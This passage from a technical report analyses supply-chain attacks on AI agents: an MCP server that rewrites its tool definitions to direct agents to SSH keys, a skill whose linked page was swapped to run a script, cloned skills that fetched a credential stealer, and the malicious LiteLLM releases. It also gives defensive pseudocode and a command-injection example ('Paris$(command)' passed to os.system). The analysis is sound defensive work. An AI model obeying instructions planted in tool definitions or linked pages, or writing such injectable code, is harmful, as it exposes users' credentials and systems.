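| What the tester does | Highest count | Definitions the tester sees |
|---|---|---|
| 40 tests, each with a new server, one tool list and two calls | 2 | Harmless |
| One session with one tool list, then 80 calls | 80 | Harmless |
| One session with a tool list, three calls and a second tool list | 3 | Harmless, then malicious |

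A test for this behaviour is short:

```
test "definitions stay the same in use":
    client = connect(server)
    before = client.list_tools()
    repeat 50 times:
        client.call_tool("format_text", {text: "hello"})
    assert client.list_tools() == before
```

This would catch a threshold of three but not one of 500. As with other hidden triggers, clean runs provide no evidence about a condition that the tester never meets.

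The protocol's July 2026 rule against tool lists that vary between connections makes a second comparison possible. A tester can keep one connection in use for a long time, open a new one with the same access rights, and compare the two lists. Any difference violates the standard, and the tester can detect it without a trusted earlier copy. A server that changed its definitions for everyone at once would still pass.

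Reading the code would have been quicker than either test. The same account had published the server's source on GitHub, including the threshold and the malicious text, so a reader could have found both without calling the server. But the 17 pull requests for the remote server added only a web address to a configuration file, so a maintainer reviewing one would have had to look for the server code elsewhere.

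Published code also doesn't prove what a remote server runs, and a more careful attacker would have published a clean version while running the malicious one. In this case, Pillar's researchers sent the server ordinary text to format, watched the tool definitions change, and confirmed that the behaviour matched the published code.

Four other pull requests pointed to a hidden Python file in the user's home directory instead. A maintainer could have rejected those without knowing anything about MCP, because a shared project has little reason to run a hidden file from each contributor's machine.

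If an agent had followed the instructions, its action log would later have shown it opening a file of SSH keys in the middle of a text-formatting task. Fogel advises anyone who connected to the server to preserve the client's logs and check what the agent did after each refresh of the tool definitions. A log that records calls but not definitions would show that the agent opened the file, but not the instruction that led it to do so.

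### The AIR experiment with a linked page

A skill can become dangerous without any change to its own files. AIR, a startup, demonstrated this on real users in an experiment that The Hacker News (2026) reported in June. AIR has a commercial interest in the result because it sells a firewall that screens skills and MCP servers for agents. It announced $50 million in funding in September, according to *AI Agent Firewall Startup AIR Security Emerges From Stealth With $50 Million* (Townsend, 2026).

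AIR wrote a skill called `brand-landingpage`, which helped people without technical training build a web page with Google's design tool Stitch. The experiment went as follows:

1. AIR submitted the skill to a GitHub repository with 156 skills and about 36,000 stars, which are bookmarks that people often read as a sign of quality. The maintainers accepted it after a few days, and the skill was then listed with the repository's stars.
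2. AIR advertised the skill on Instagram to marketers, salespeople and designers.
3. The skill told the agent to install Stitch's developer kit by following the documentation at a link. AIR owned the linked domain, which at first led to Google's genuine documentation.
4. Once many people had installed the skill, AIR replaced the page with one that told the agent to download and run a script. The script sent the user's email address to AIR and did nothing else.

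Every scanner that AIR tried, including those from Cisco and NVIDIA, rated the skill safe. The Hacker News explains that these scanners examine only the submitted files, so they did not check the page behind the link. Scanning that page wouldn't have helped at first, because the page was still genuine.

Outsiders can check part of this account. The Hacker News does not name the repository, but a listing on the public registry skills.sh has the same skill name and a similar star count. Gen Agent Trust Hub, one of the registry's scanners, rated the listed skill safe on 2 May in *brand-landingpage* (2026), although it noted that the skill had the agent install outside software. The scanner had also passed an earlier copy on 23 April, when it described the linked domain, stitch-design.ai, as the vendor's own.

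The scanner had therefore detected the link but misidentified its owner. Google hosts Stitch under withgoogle.com, so checking who owned the linked domain might have raised a doubt before AIR changed anything. But no scan of the skill's files could have revealed what the page would contain a month later.

### How many agents the AIR skill reached

AIR says the skill reached about 26,000 agents, some on corporate accounts. Nobody outside the firm has confirmed this. Constantin (2026), in *A fake AI agent skill passed every security scanner*, repeats the number but takes it from The Hacker News.

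The public install counters show totals of the same order of magnitude. Claude Marketplaces' *brand-landingpage*, a directory entry, showed 25,400 installs in mid-May, before AIR published its results, so those installs can't have come from people reading about the results. By early July, skills.sh's *brand-landingpage* (2026) showed 27,500. Claude Marketplaces may copy its count from skills.sh, so the two counts are best treated as one piece of evidence.

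An install is not the same as an agent that ran the script. According to The Hacker News, AIR counted agents by the email addresses that the script sent back. If both numbers are right and the counter is complete, then

26,000 agents / 27,500 installs ≈ 95%

This would mean that nearly everyone who installed the skill used it after the page changed, and nearly every agent followed the new instructions. Those rates seem high for a free tool that people found through an advertisement. The counter may have missed people who downloaded the whole repository, or AIR may have counted more loosely than the account suggests. AIR also claims that it could have taken full control of every agent, but that would have depended on each agent's permissions.

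In May, skills.sh listed the earlier copy of the skill with only 64 installs and two stars. The popular repository and the advertisement evidently made a large difference, though the numbers aren't enough to separate their effects.

Skills whose authors are honest have the same weakness, because anyone can buy an expired domain that a skill links to and decide what the skill's users will read there. *Partnering with Air*, by AIR's investor Sequoia Capital, describes a second project in which AIR found 925 published skills that depended on dead links. AIR registered the abandoned addresses and says that this gave it control of roughly 134,000 agents, a figure that is also unconfirmed.

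AIR's skill would have passed a functional test both before and after the change, because it produced a landing page each time. The agent's log would have shown it fetching the documentation, then downloading and running a script. Installing a genuine developer kit can look much the same, so a monitor that flagged every such download would also flag legitimate skills. A monitor that restricted what the script could read and where it could send data would probably have worked better.

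### The cloned skills on skills.sh

In July 2026 an attacker published copies of the skills that belong to Paperclip, a popular AI tool, and later made them malicious. The main account is Zenity Labs' *Attackers Target Agents via The Skill Supply Chain*, from the research group of a company that sells security for AI agents. Its timeline shows how long the skills were harmless:

| Date in 2026 | Event |
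|---|---|
| 2 July | The attacker copies Paperclip's source code to a GitHub organisation with a similar name |
| 5 July | The copied skills appear on skills.sh, identical to the originals. One already shows 2,264 installs |
| 6 July | The attacker adds malicious code to the copied program but not to the skills |
| 11 July | The attacker adds a malicious installation guide to the skills, which are among the registry's trending items the same day |
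| 13 and 20 July | The attacker uploads two related packages to PyPI. Defenders spot the first in under two hours and the second within one |
| 1 August | Zenity notices the skills |
| 2 August | Vercel, which runs skills.sh, and GitHub remove them within 12 hours of Zenity's report |

Anyone who compared the skills with Paperclip's originals before 11 July would have found no difference. After that date, an auditor who read only the main file of each skill could still have missed the problem, because those files described legitimate tasks. The harmful command was in a separate installation guide, which the agent was to open only when Paperclip needed installing. Some of the skills referred the agent to another skill that contained the guide, so an auditor had to read every file and follow every reference.

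The guide told the agent to fetch a program from the attacker's server and run it. On a Mac or Linux machine, the program searched 127 places for passwords, keys and other credentials, and sent the attacker what it found. The attacker could replace the program on the server at any time without changing the skills again. Researchers have also shown that skills can cause harm through written instructions, with no malicious code to download.

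The registry's counters for the family added up to more than 1.7 million installs by the beginning of August. Zenity Labs stresses that these are not users and that the number of victims is unknown. Much of the total probably comes from counting the same installation several times. The family had six skills in the trending list on 11 July, and several individual counters later stood near 300,000. If people usually installed all six together, then

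1.7 million / 6 ≈ 283,000 installations

which is close to what the individual counters showed. Even this is not a count of people, since automated systems can install the same skill repeatedly, and it includes installations from before the skills turned malicious.

The malicious skills stayed up for about three weeks, while defenders spotted each PyPI package within hours. This may be partly because the packages contained the stealing code itself, which malware scanners can recognise, whereas the skills contained an instruction to fetch it. Even after detection, PyPI recorded downloads of both packages until 26 July.

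The code in the second PyPI package's GitHub repository looked harmless, but the automated release process ignored it and published a file that the attacker had uploaded by hand. Someone reading the repository would not have seen the code that users installed, even if a provenance attestation correctly named the repository and the release process. Deadbugz was easier to audit because its operator had published the malicious version.

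### What tests and monitoring could have found in the clones

On 6 July, the attacker added code to the copied Paperclip program and hid it in a function named as if it kept a log. Three ordinary operations called this function before doing their work, so it ran whether or not they succeeded, and any errors in it went unreported. A test that checked an operation's result would have passed.

The function also ran only once in each working directory, leaving a file there to mark that it had run. Repeating the tests in the same directory would therefore have produced no suspicious activity. With Deadbugz, by contrast, starting afresh kept the tester from seeing the malicious text. Testing for both kinds of trigger requires some runs in a clean environment and others in one that has been in use for a while, with network traffic and file access recorded from the first run onwards.

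Zenity found the campaign by running a large batch of skills in an isolated environment and observing what they did, a method called detonation. This captured the program that the attacker's server sent and recorded it collecting credentials. It worked only because the attacker's server was active and the agent reached the installation guide. A detonation on 5 July would have shown nothing, so a registry would need to repeat the test whenever a skill changes, and occasionally even if it hasn't changed.

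Zenity Labs recommends that people who had already installed the skills search records of outgoing network traffic for requests to the attacker's domain. Only organisations that were already keeping such records can do this. Removing the skills from the registry also leaves installed copies in place, so users still have to delete them by hand, as TechRadar's *Experts warn malicious AI skills are hitting more victims than ever* points out.

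### Fingerprinting definitions

The remedy that Fogel recommends for Deadbugz is to record a fingerprint of each tool definition when the user approves it and to compare it with later versions. The fingerprint can be a hash, as in the pinning of packages. A client could implement it like this:

```
when the user approves a server:
    for each tool in server.list_tools():
        approved_text[tool.name] = tool.definition
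        approved_hash[tool.name] = sha256(normalise(tool.definition))

whenever a new tool list arrives:
    for each tool in the list:
        if the tool has no approved hash, or
           sha256(normalise(tool.definition)) != approved_hash[tool.name]:
            withhold the new definition from the model
            show the user the old and new text, and ask
```

The `normalise` step puts the fields in a fixed order and removes meaningless spacing, so the same definition always gives the same hash. The client also keeps the approved text because a hash shows only that something changed, and the user needs to see what changed.

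The hash has to cover the tool's complete definition, because a hash of the description alone would miss a new input field whose name could lead the model to fill in private data. The client should also compare hashes for every tool list it receives, including after it reconnects, rather than wait for a change notice, which a malicious server's operator can omit.

Against Deadbugz, the client would have stored the harmless definitions at approval. After the third call, it would have received the altered list, calculated a different hash and stopped before the model read the new text. The user would then have seen that the new text for a text-formatting tool included an instruction for the agent to look for SSH keys. The client can do this without a list of suspicious words and without judging whether the text is malicious.

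Prompts are harder to protect because a server can build them from information the client supplies, so their text may legitimately differ each time. A client could fingerprint fixed prompts and treat variable ones as untrusted text. Fingerprinting only tools would have missed the half of Deadbugz that arrived through prompts.

The same method works for skills if the hash covers every file in the folder and any other skill those files refer to. Someone who installed a Paperclip clone on 5 July and updated it after 11 July would have received a warning, but anyone who first installed it on 12 July would have fingerprinted the malicious version.

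### Changes that a fingerprint misses

Fingerprints detect changes only in the text that the client has hashed:

| Case | What changed | Would the fingerprint differ? |
|---|---|---|
| Deadbugz | Tool definitions and prompts | Yes for the definitions. For prompts, only if the client hashes them |
| Invariant Labs' demonstration | A tool's description | Yes |
| skills.sh clones | Files in the skill folders | Yes, for people who had installed the clean version |
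| AIR's skill | A page that the skill linked to | No |
| `postmark-mcp` | Code behind an unchanged definition | No |

Pinning covers the last case for a local package until the user updates, but not for a remote server.

The operator of `productivity-suite` could instead have left the tool definitions unchanged and put the same instructions in the output of `summarize`, which the model also reads. The client can't check a summary against an approved version, because each summary is supposed to be new.

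Linked pages fall between these two. A client could hash the page at approval, but software documentation changes often, so most of the alarms would be false. A reviewer could instead copy the necessary instructions into the skill, fix the developer kit to an exact version and remove the link. The skill would then keep working as it did when it was reviewed. But someone would have to update it by hand whenever the software changed, and AIR's skill included an instruction for agents to trust the online documentation because the developer kit was new and still changing.

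Fogel also recommends fixed rules for reading sensitive files, running code and sending email, which would apply whatever a tool's definition tells the agent to do. These rules would partly fill the gaps above. They also cover instructions that arrive in a tool result or a web page, because the agent still has to carry out the harmful action. They do not stop a server whose own code steals data, as in `postmark-mcp`.

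### The cost of asking again

Fogel wants clients to require renewed approval before a changed tool can influence sensitive actions. But most changes to definitions are harmless, such as spelling corrections, added examples and descriptions of new options. If a user has ten servers and each changes a definition once a month, the user will get 120 prompts a year. If one change in a thousand is malicious, the user will see one about every eight years. By then many people will approve changes without reading them, as users of agents already do with individual tool calls.

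Asking the user to approve changes is also better than asking about every call. In this invented example, an agent that makes 100 calls a day would generate 36,500 approval requests a year if it asked about every call, about 300 times as many as if it asked only about changes. A request about a changed definition also shows the user the text that matters, which a request about a call does not.

Normalising the definitions already removes alarms about formatting, and a client can reduce the number further by combining all the changes from one update into a single request. It can also highlight the words that differ. If a server writes today's date or the names of the user's projects into its descriptions, a plain hash would trigger an alarm every time one of these details changed. The server's author could avoid this by moving such details into the tool's results, although the client can't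 fingerprint them there.

The client also doesn't have to interrupt the user at once. If the tool's inputs haven't changed, it can keep giving the model the old, approved definition while the new one waits for review. With Deadbugz, the agent could have kept formatting text without ever receiving the malicious instructions. If the inputs have changed, calls based on the old definition may fail, so the client has to suspend the tool or ask the user.

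In a company, one person can review each change for everybody. One approved hash can cover all users with the same access rights, since they should all receive the same tool list. The reviewer has more time and probably more expertise than a designer who wants to finish a web page. But every update has to wait until the reviewer gets to it, including updates that fix a dangerous mistake in the old text.

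## The compromised LiteLLM releases of March 2026

On 24 March 2026, attackers uploaded two malicious versions of the legitimate and very popular LiteLLM project to PyPI, apparently with publishing credentials stolen from the project's build process. By contrast, the people who published `postmark-mcp`, the Deadbugz server and the cloned skills controlled those components from the start.

LiteLLM is a Python library that lets a program send requests to many companies' language models in a single format. This makes it easy to switch providers, so developers of agent frameworks and MCP servers build on it, and people who install their software get LiteLLM too. Companies can also run it as a proxy, a server that forwards all their model requests. LiteLLM is normally installed 15 to 20 million times a week, according to PyPI's *Incident Report* (2026). Researchers at the security firm Sonatype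 point out in Help Net Security's *LiteLLM PyPI packages compromised in expanding TeamPCP supply chain attacks* (2026) that it is an attractive target because it often has access to the user's keys for several model providers.

### From a security scanner to PyPI

A build pipeline is a series of automatic steps that test a project's code, package it and publish it. One step in LiteLLM's pipeline ran Trivy, an open-source scanner from Aqua Security that looks for known vulnerabilities. LiteLLM's maintainers believe that the attack came through this scanner:

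1. In late February, attackers exploited a misconfigured workflow in Trivy's GitHub repository and stole an access token, according to Akamai's *The Telnyx SDK on PyPI Compromise* (2026).
2. Aqua disclosed a breach on 1 March and replaced its credentials, but not all at once. In Help Net Security's account, the company explains that the attackers could have used a token that still worked to steal the new credentials.
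3. On 19 March, a criminal group called TeamPCP published a malicious version of Trivy. It also changed the code behind 76 of the 77 version labels of Trivy's GitHub Action, a ready-made step that runs the scanner in a pipeline. GitLab's *Pipeline security lessons from March supply chain incidents* (2026) describes how the new code collected passwords and keys from the pipelines that ran it.
4. LiteLLM's pipeline requested Trivy without specifying a version and ran a malicious copy. Dholakia and Jaff (2026), in *Security Townhall Updates*, explain that all the pipeline's steps shared one environment, which also held LiteLLM's permanent publishing credentials. The scanner could therefore read them.
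5. On 24 March, the attackers uploaded LiteLLM 1.82.7 and 1.82.8 directly to PyPI. The project's GitHub page had no matching release.

Dholakia and Jaff, who run LiteLLM, say their current understanding is that the stolen credentials came from Trivy. LiteLLM initially suspected that someone had taken over a maintainer's PyPI account (*Security Update*, 2026). PyPI also says the credentials came from Trivy, though it may be relying on what the maintainers told it.

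### Code that runs before any test

Both versions contained the same malware but triggered it differently. In 1.82.7, the malware was in the proxy server file, and Datadog Security Labs' *LiteLLM and Telnyx compromised on PyPI* (2026) advises defenders to focus on systems that loaded that file. A program that used 1.82.7 only to send requests may not have run the malware.

Version 1.82.8 also included a file called `litellm_init.pth`. Python reads the `.pth` files in its package folder every time it starts. These files usually list extra folders to search for code, but Python also executes any line in them that begins with `import`. The malware therefore ran whenever Python started in that environment, even for a program that did not use LiteLLM.

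Suppose a developer installs 1.82.8 and runs the project's tests before accepting it:

1. The installer copies LiteLLM's files, including `litellm_init.pth`, into the package folder.
2. The developer types `pytest`, the name of a common test program. It is written in Python, so Python starts.
3. Python reads `litellm_init.pth` and launches the malware as a separate process.
4. Python loads `pytest`, which looks for the tests and runs them.

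The malware starts searching the machine before the first test runs, so no assertion can prevent the search. Replacing LiteLLM with a mock does not prevent it either, because the malicious file is still in the package folder.

The malware collected SSH keys, cloud credentials, database passwords, command history and cryptocurrency wallets. It encrypted this data and sent it to `models.litellm.cloud`, a domain that does not belong to LiteLLM. It also installed a background service that could download more programs, so removing the package did not clean the machine. If it found suitable credentials for Kubernetes, a system for running software on many machines, it tried to spread to all of those machines.

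### The crash at FutureSearch

Callum McMahon of the AI company FutureSearch found the malware because a bug in it slowed his Mac until he had to force a restart. He had started a local MCP server in the code editor Cursor, and the server pulled in the newest LiteLLM release as a transitive dependency. The release was minutes old, according to InfoQ's *PyPI Supply Chain Attack Compromises LiteLLM, Enabling the Exfiltration of Sensitive Information*.

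The malware launched a second Python process to run its code. That process also read the `.pth` file at startup, so it launched another, and the number of processes grew until the machine crashed. FutureSearch's *litellm 1.82.8 Supply Chain Attack on PyPI (March 2026)* (2026) describes how the company traced the cause with help from Claude Code, an AI coding agent, and reported it to PyPI and LiteLLM's maintainers.

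The AI researcher Andrej Karpathy argued that the malware would have gone unnoticed for much longer without this bug. The next attack suggests that the bug might have sped up detection only a little. On 27 March the same group published malicious versions of `telnyx`, a package for telephone services. PyPI received the first report after an hour and 45 minutes, compared with an hour and 19 minutes for LiteLLM. But by then researchers knew about the campaign and were probably watching for more attacks.

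Someone also tried to suppress the warning. According to FutureSearch, the owner's account closed the public discussion of the problem on GitHub as "not planned", and hundreds of bots flooded it with messages. The company concluded that the attackers had very likely taken over the maintainer's account. A user who checked the project's page that afternoon could have thought the maintainers had dismissed the report.

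### How long the releases were available

LiteLLM and PyPI give very different exposure times. Their accounts and FutureSearch's produce this timeline for 24 March:

| Time (UTC) | Event |
|---|---|
| 10:39 | Version 1.82.7 appears on PyPI |
| 10:52 | Version 1.82.8 appears |
| About 11:58 | PyPI receives the first report |
| About 13:11 | PyPI quarantines LiteLLM, which stops new downloads |
| By 16:00 | PyPI and LiteLLM have deleted both versions |
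| 16:15 | The public database OSV lists them as malicious |

The two approximate times come from adding PyPI's intervals to 10:39. PyPI puts the total exposure at 2 hours and 32 minutes, including 1 hour and 12 minutes between the first report and the quarantine. LiteLLM says the packages were available for about 40 minutes from 10:39, which would mean PyPI quarantined them at about 11:19, before anyone had reported them.

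PyPI's figure is more credible because PyPI runs the registry and imposed the quarantine. Its download count also supports the longer time. PyPI counted more than 119,000 downloads of the malicious versions, and LiteLLM normally has about 1,700 installs a minute:

1,700 × 40 minutes = 68,000 installs

1,700 × 152 minutes ≈ 258,000 installs

Forty minutes would have been too short for 119,000 downloads unless traffic was much heavier than usual. That figure may originally have been the time between McMahon's report and the quarantine, which InfoQ puts at about 40 minutes and PyPI at an hour and 12 minutes. InfoQ also gives a lower count of over 40,000 downloads, perhaps because it covers only one of the versions.

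The same numbers underlie PyPI's estimate that 40% to 50% of LiteLLM installs were unpinned:

119,000 / 258,000 ≈ 46%

PyPI assumes that traffic during the attack was average for the week. The result is a share of installs, not of users or projects.

The number of victims is uncertain too. In August the security firm Hudson Rock analysed a 153 GB archive of data from the attack and linked it to 2,488 company domains, according to Help Net Security's *LiteLLM hit by second supply chain attack this year* (2026). Another vendor, CloudSEK, put the number of exposed organisations at close to 2,500. A company's domain can appear in stolen files even if the company never installed LiteLLM, for example in a supplier's saved login.

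### Scanning for known advisories

OSV's *Two litellm versions published containing credential harvesting malware* (2026) appeared five and a half hours after the first upload and about three hours after the quarantine. A scanner that relied on OSV would have passed both versions for as long as people could install them from PyPI.

As with `postmark-mcp`, the advisory could still help to find installed copies. FutureSearch advised users to empty their installers' caches, because an installer can reinstall a downloaded package from its cache after the registry has deleted it.

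Advisories can also take much longer. On 9 September 2026, attackers published a malicious version of the MCP server package `@dforge-core/dforge-mcp`. CloudSEK's report of 20 September found no advisory for it in OSV or GitHub's database, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Attackers Abuse npm Trusted Publishing in GHAPPIER Campaign* (2026).

### Pinning and lock files

LiteLLM's official Docker image, a ready-to-run copy of the proxy with its dependencies, did not include the malicious releases because its configuration pinned exact versions.

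McMahon's case shows that a tool's dependencies need to be pinned too. If he had pinned only the MCP server, it would still have downloaded the newest LiteLLM. A lock file records the exact version and a hash of every package that a project installs, including transitive dependencies. PyPI points out that the common command `pip freeze` doesn't produce a lock file, because it records versions without hashes.

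Pinning a version number would have been enough to avoid LiteLLM 1.82.8, but not the malicious Trivy code. GitHub lets a project's owner move a version tag to different code, and TeamPCP moved 76 tags. A pipeline that requested one of them would have received the malware without any change to its own configuration. Pinning the commit hash instead would have kept the pipeline on the old version.

Developers still have to update the lock file from time to time, and anyone who did so between 10:39 and 13:11 on 24 March could have locked the malicious version along with its correct hash. CloudSEK therefore advises users of the dforge package to treat any lock file that names its malicious version as a sign of compromise.

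### Waiting periods and their cost

A waiting period, or cooldown, makes an installer ignore any release younger than a certain age. PyPI gives this example of a three-day wait for the installer uv:

```
[tool.uv]
exclude-newer = "P3D"
```

With this setting, LiteLLM 1.82.8 would have become eligible for installation at 10:52 on 27 March, almost three days after PyPI quarantined it. A one-day wait would also have been long enough for both LiteLLM and Telnyx, which PyPI quarantined after 3 hours and 42 minutes. Neither wait would have been long enough for `postmark-mcp`.

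The drawback is that security fixes wait too. Suppose the maintainers of a library fix a serious flaw at 09:00 on Monday, and attackers start exploiting it at 09:00 on Tuesday. Three teams use the library and install each release as soon as their settings allow:

| Waiting period | Fix installed | Time exposed to attacks | Would it have blocked LiteLLM 1.82.8? |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | Monday 09:00 | None | No |
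| One day | Tuesday 09:00 | None | Yes |
| Three days | Thursday 09:00 | Two days | Yes |

If w is the waiting period and e is the time between the fix and the first attacks, the waiting period leaves the team exposed for

max(0, w − e)

A malicious release can be installed only if it stays available for longer than the wait, w. The wait should therefore be at least as long as defenders need to remove malware and no longer than attackers need to exploit a flaw after its fix is published. One day meets both conditions in this example. If attackers exploit the flaw as soon as the fix is public, or earlier, every hour of waiting adds an hour of exposure.

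Late fixes may have contributed to a second attack on LiteLLM. On 21 October 2026, attackers published the malicious version 1.107.0, which stayed on PyPI for an hour and 44 minutes. Help Net Security reports that LiteLLM suspects the attackers entered one of its internal systems through a recently patched vulnerability. The company hasn't confirmed this, and nothing suggests that a waiting period delayed the patch.

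Teams can get security fixes sooner by exempting them from the wait. Dependabot and Renovate, two services that propose updates, do this by default. They exempt only releases identified as security fixes, so a fix that the maintainers publish without an advisory may still be delayed. A developer can also override the wait for a single package.

Security firms scan new releases automatically, so they could still discover malware if every user waited three days to install. They spotted the October version within six minutes, according to the Italian news site TecnoAndroid's *LiteLLM compromesso* (2026). Users might no longer discover malware themselves if everyone waited, since McMahon found it only because his machine had installed it immediately. The firms probably check obscure packages less quickly than LiteLLM, so waiting may be less effective for a little-known MCP server.

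### Comparing a package with its source

Researchers at Endor Labs, another security vendor, found that the malicious code was in the packages on PyPI but not in LiteLLM's GitHub repository, according to ITPro's *LiteLLM PyPI compromise*. An auditor could have discovered this in four steps:

1. Download the package without installing it.
2. Find the release with the same version number on GitHub.
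3. List the files that are in the package but not in the source.
4. Compare the contents of the files that are in both.

The audit would have stopped at step 2 for 1.82.8, because GitHub had no such release. That is a good reason not to install the package yet, though it doesn't prove an attack by itself, since some maintainers publish a package before they tag the source.

LiteLLM later used a similar method to check its older releases. For versions 1.78.0 to 1.82.6, it calculated each package's hash, searched for known traces of the malware and compared the contents with the corresponding source code. It found no sign of tampering.

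The October release would have passed step 2, because version 1.107.0 had a matching label on GitHub and the code there was clean. *Top CI/CD Security Incidents*, by StepSecurity, a firm that sells security for build pipelines, describes how one added line in the build configuration put three extra files into each of the seven installable packages. These included a `.pth` file, as in March. Step 3 would have revealed all three files. Compiled programs are harder to check because the auditor has to repeat the build, and the result may not be identical.

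Comparing a published package with its source repository does not reveal an attack if the attackers changed the source. In October 2026, attackers added malicious files to the main branch of Tensorlake, another software project, and its normal release process published them to npm. StepSecurity notes that the npm package matched the repository because both contained the malicious files.

### What provenance attestations would have shown

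Provenance attestations, which record a package's source and build process, work well with PyPI's Trusted Publishers system. The registry accepts uploads from a particular pipeline and gives it a short-lived token for each release, so the project doesn't have to store a permanent password. Someone who steals an old password and uploads a package from elsewhere can't produce the same attestation.

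LiteLLM still used permanent credentials in March and apparently published no attestations. Users would have seen no difference between a clean version and a malicious one, and a rule requiring attestations would have rejected both. PyPI reports that LiteLLM adopted Trusted Publishers after the attack, but StepSecurity reports that LiteLLM's packages still had no attestations in October.

A similar theft affected the coding agent Cline in February 2026. The Hacker News (2026) reports that someone used a stolen npm token to publish version 2.3.0 of its command-line program. The only change was an installation script that installed OpenClaw, a separate AI agent, alongside Cline. The release was downloaded about 4,000 times in the eight hours before the maintainers replaced it. The damage was small because OpenClaw is not malicious, but the attacker could have used the same script to install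 malware.

The token had probably leaked through an AI agent that Cline used to sort incoming bug reports on GitHub. The researcher Adnan Khan had found that instructions in a report's title could make the agent run commands. An attacker could then tamper with files that the release process reused and steal the publishing token.

After such incidents, Henrik Plate of Endor Labs advises users to watch for releases that suddenly lack attestations. That check would have exposed Cline 2.3.0 only if earlier releases had attestations, which is unclear because Cline announced support for token-free publishing after the attack. Adding token-free publishing alone would not have been enough, because a thief could still use the old tokens. Plate therefore also recommends disabling them.

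In September 2026, attackers compromised two packages from MemTensor, which makes memory software for AI agents. The Hacker News' *Compromised MemTensor Packages Deliver sckit Credential Stealer via npm and PyPI* (2026) lists three malicious versions of a plugin for OpenClaw and one of the Python package MemoryOS. The plugin ran the malware when OpenClaw's gateway started and again whenever the agent recalled a memory, and it passed the user's prompt to the malware. A test of memory recall could therefore pass while triggering the theft. There were no installation scripts, so disabling them would not have helped. But the plugin had grown from 272 KB to 43.6 MB, which even a crude audit could have detected.

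Reports differ on how the attackers published the packages. The security firm SafeDep says they added code to MemTensor's release pipelines that captured the publishing tokens. Antipov (2026), in *Один червь одновременно захватил npm и PyPI*, adds that they worked in short-lived branches and that nobody has confirmed how they gained access. According to SC Media's *MemTensor npm, PyPI packages compromised with cross-platform credential stealer*, Socket, another firm, concluded from the absence of the usual record of a source commit that the npm releases did not come from the normal pipeline. Both accounts can be right if the attackers stole the tokens inside the pipeline and used them outside it. The releases would then have had no valid attestation from the pipeline, and a user accustomed to seeing one could have noticed.

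Attackers who publish from inside a project's pipeline get a valid attestation. In May 2026, attackers did this with 84 versions of packages from TanStack, a popular set of JavaScript libraries. The Hacker News' *Mini Shai-Hulud Worm Compromises TanStack, Mistral AI, Guardrails AI & More Packages* (2026) explains that the attackers extracted a short-lived token from the memory of the running build. The attackers of the dforge MCP server could already change its main branch, so they used the project's own pipeline to publish their code.

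| Release | How the attackers published it | Would an attestation have exposed it? |
|---|---|---|
| LiteLLM 1.82.7 and 1.82.8 | Stolen credentials, used outside the pipeline | No, because clean releases apparently had none either |
| Cline CLI 2.3.0 | Stolen token, used outside the pipeline | Yes, if earlier releases had attestations |
| MemTensor | Tokens from the pipeline, probably used outside it | Yes, if earlier releases had attestations |
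| TanStack | Short-lived token from a running build | No, the attestation was valid |
| dforge MCP server | Malicious source, published by the normal pipeline | No, the attestation was valid |

In the October attack on LiteLLM, the attackers made the pipeline build from a repository called `Berri-AI/litellm` instead of the genuine `BerriAI/litellm`. The build record for the Docker image contained the false name. A person could easily have overlooked the extra hyphen, but a program that compared the name with the expected one would have rejected the image.

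### Searching build logs for the affected versions

After the March attack, companies had to find out which of their machines had installed the malicious versions. Build servers usually log each job, including the packages it installed. LiteLLM published two user-contributed scripts that search these logs on GitHub and GitLab. Each script downloads the logs of jobs that ran during a certain period and looks for `litellm` followed by one of the two version numbers.

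The scripts have three weaknesses that could make an affected company look clean:

- By default they search only jobs that started between 08:00 and 12:44. PyPI's figures put the quarantine at about 13:11. At an average rate, around 21,000 of the 119,000 downloads would have taken place in those last 27 minutes. A user who corrected the date but not the hours would have missed them.
- The search pattern allows only one character between the name and the number. It finds `litellm-1.82.8`, which the installer pip prints, but not `litellm==1.82.8`, which uv prints.
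- If a job's log is no longer available, the script treats the job as if it had not installed LiteLLM.

A better script would search until 16:00, the end of the period in which LiteLLM tells users to consider themselves at risk. It would accept both formats and list every job whose log was missing. Even then it would cover only build servers and miss machines such as McMahon's laptop. Datadog also recommends searching for the malware's files and for connections to its domains, which can reveal infections that an installation log misses.

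LiteLLM's maintainers could have run the same kind of search before the attack. According to Akamai, news outlets reported the Trivy compromise on 19 March, five days before the malicious LiteLLM releases. If the maintainers had searched their build logs for the affected Trivy versions, they might have replaced their publishing credentials in time. How much time they had depends on when the malicious scan ran, which they haven't disclosed.

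### Auditing tools are dependencies too

The attackers obtained LiteLLM's publishing credentials through the compromised scanner Trivy, which LiteLLM ran to make its software safer. On 23 March the same group also compromised KICS, a scanner from the security company Checkmarx. Kiran Raj of Endor Labs, quoted in ITPro, believes the group deliberately chooses such tools because they run in places likely to contain valuable credentials.

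A scanner needs to read the code it checks but doesn't need the password used to publish it. After the attack, Dholakia and Jaff announced that LiteLLM would run its unit tests, integration tests, security scans and publishing in four separate environments. This separation would probably have kept the publishing credentials from Trivy, even if the scanner was malicious. Pinning Trivy to the hash of a clean version would have prevented the malicious version from running. A pinned scanner still needs a current list of known vulnerabilities, but a team can usually update the list without updating the program.

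Even these stronger controls did not prevent the October attack. *LiteLLM*, in the German trade magazine IT-Administrator, describes a release process that only one account could use, and only on a particular office laptop. Earlier in the week of the attack, however, the team had temporarily given two engineers wider release rights so they could send customers daily bug fixes.

The attackers had the GitHub tokens of three engineers. They used one account to change the release process, another to approve the release and the third to delete the records of their actions. LiteLLM believes they took the tokens from the logs of its internal LiteLLM server, which anyone on the internet could reach. The company has found that Claude Code sometimes includes a user's GitHub token in a response, and a LiteLLM server that logs responses also stores the token.

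## What a dependency audit of 48,682 agent skills found

Malicious releases like LiteLLM's are rare. More often, a skill still uses an old library version with an accidental flaw. *Carried-Over and Agent-Native Threats in the Supply Chain of LLM Agent Skills* (Li, Guo and colleagues, 2026) measured how many skills on ClawHub have accidental flaws and how many of those flaws an attacker could exploit through an agent. The team copied the whole registry in March 2026, with 48,682 skills by 17,130 authors. About 44% of the skills contained code, and the rest were written instructions only.

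The researchers assumed that the skill's author is honest and that the attacker controls only something the agent reads during a task, such as an email or a web page. Planting instructions there is called indirect prompt injection. Suppose a travel skill contains this line, simplified from a real one on ClawHub:

```
os.system("search_flights --city " + city)
```

The agent takes the city from an email. If the attacker's email gives the destination as `Paris$(command)`, the operating system runs the text in parentheses as a command before the skill searches for flights. The skill's author meant no harm but forgot to check the input.

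### How the researchers searched

1. They matched the library versions that each skill declares against the advisories in OSV. This is software composition analysis, and it was possible for the 3,188 skills with a Python requirements file or an npm lock file.
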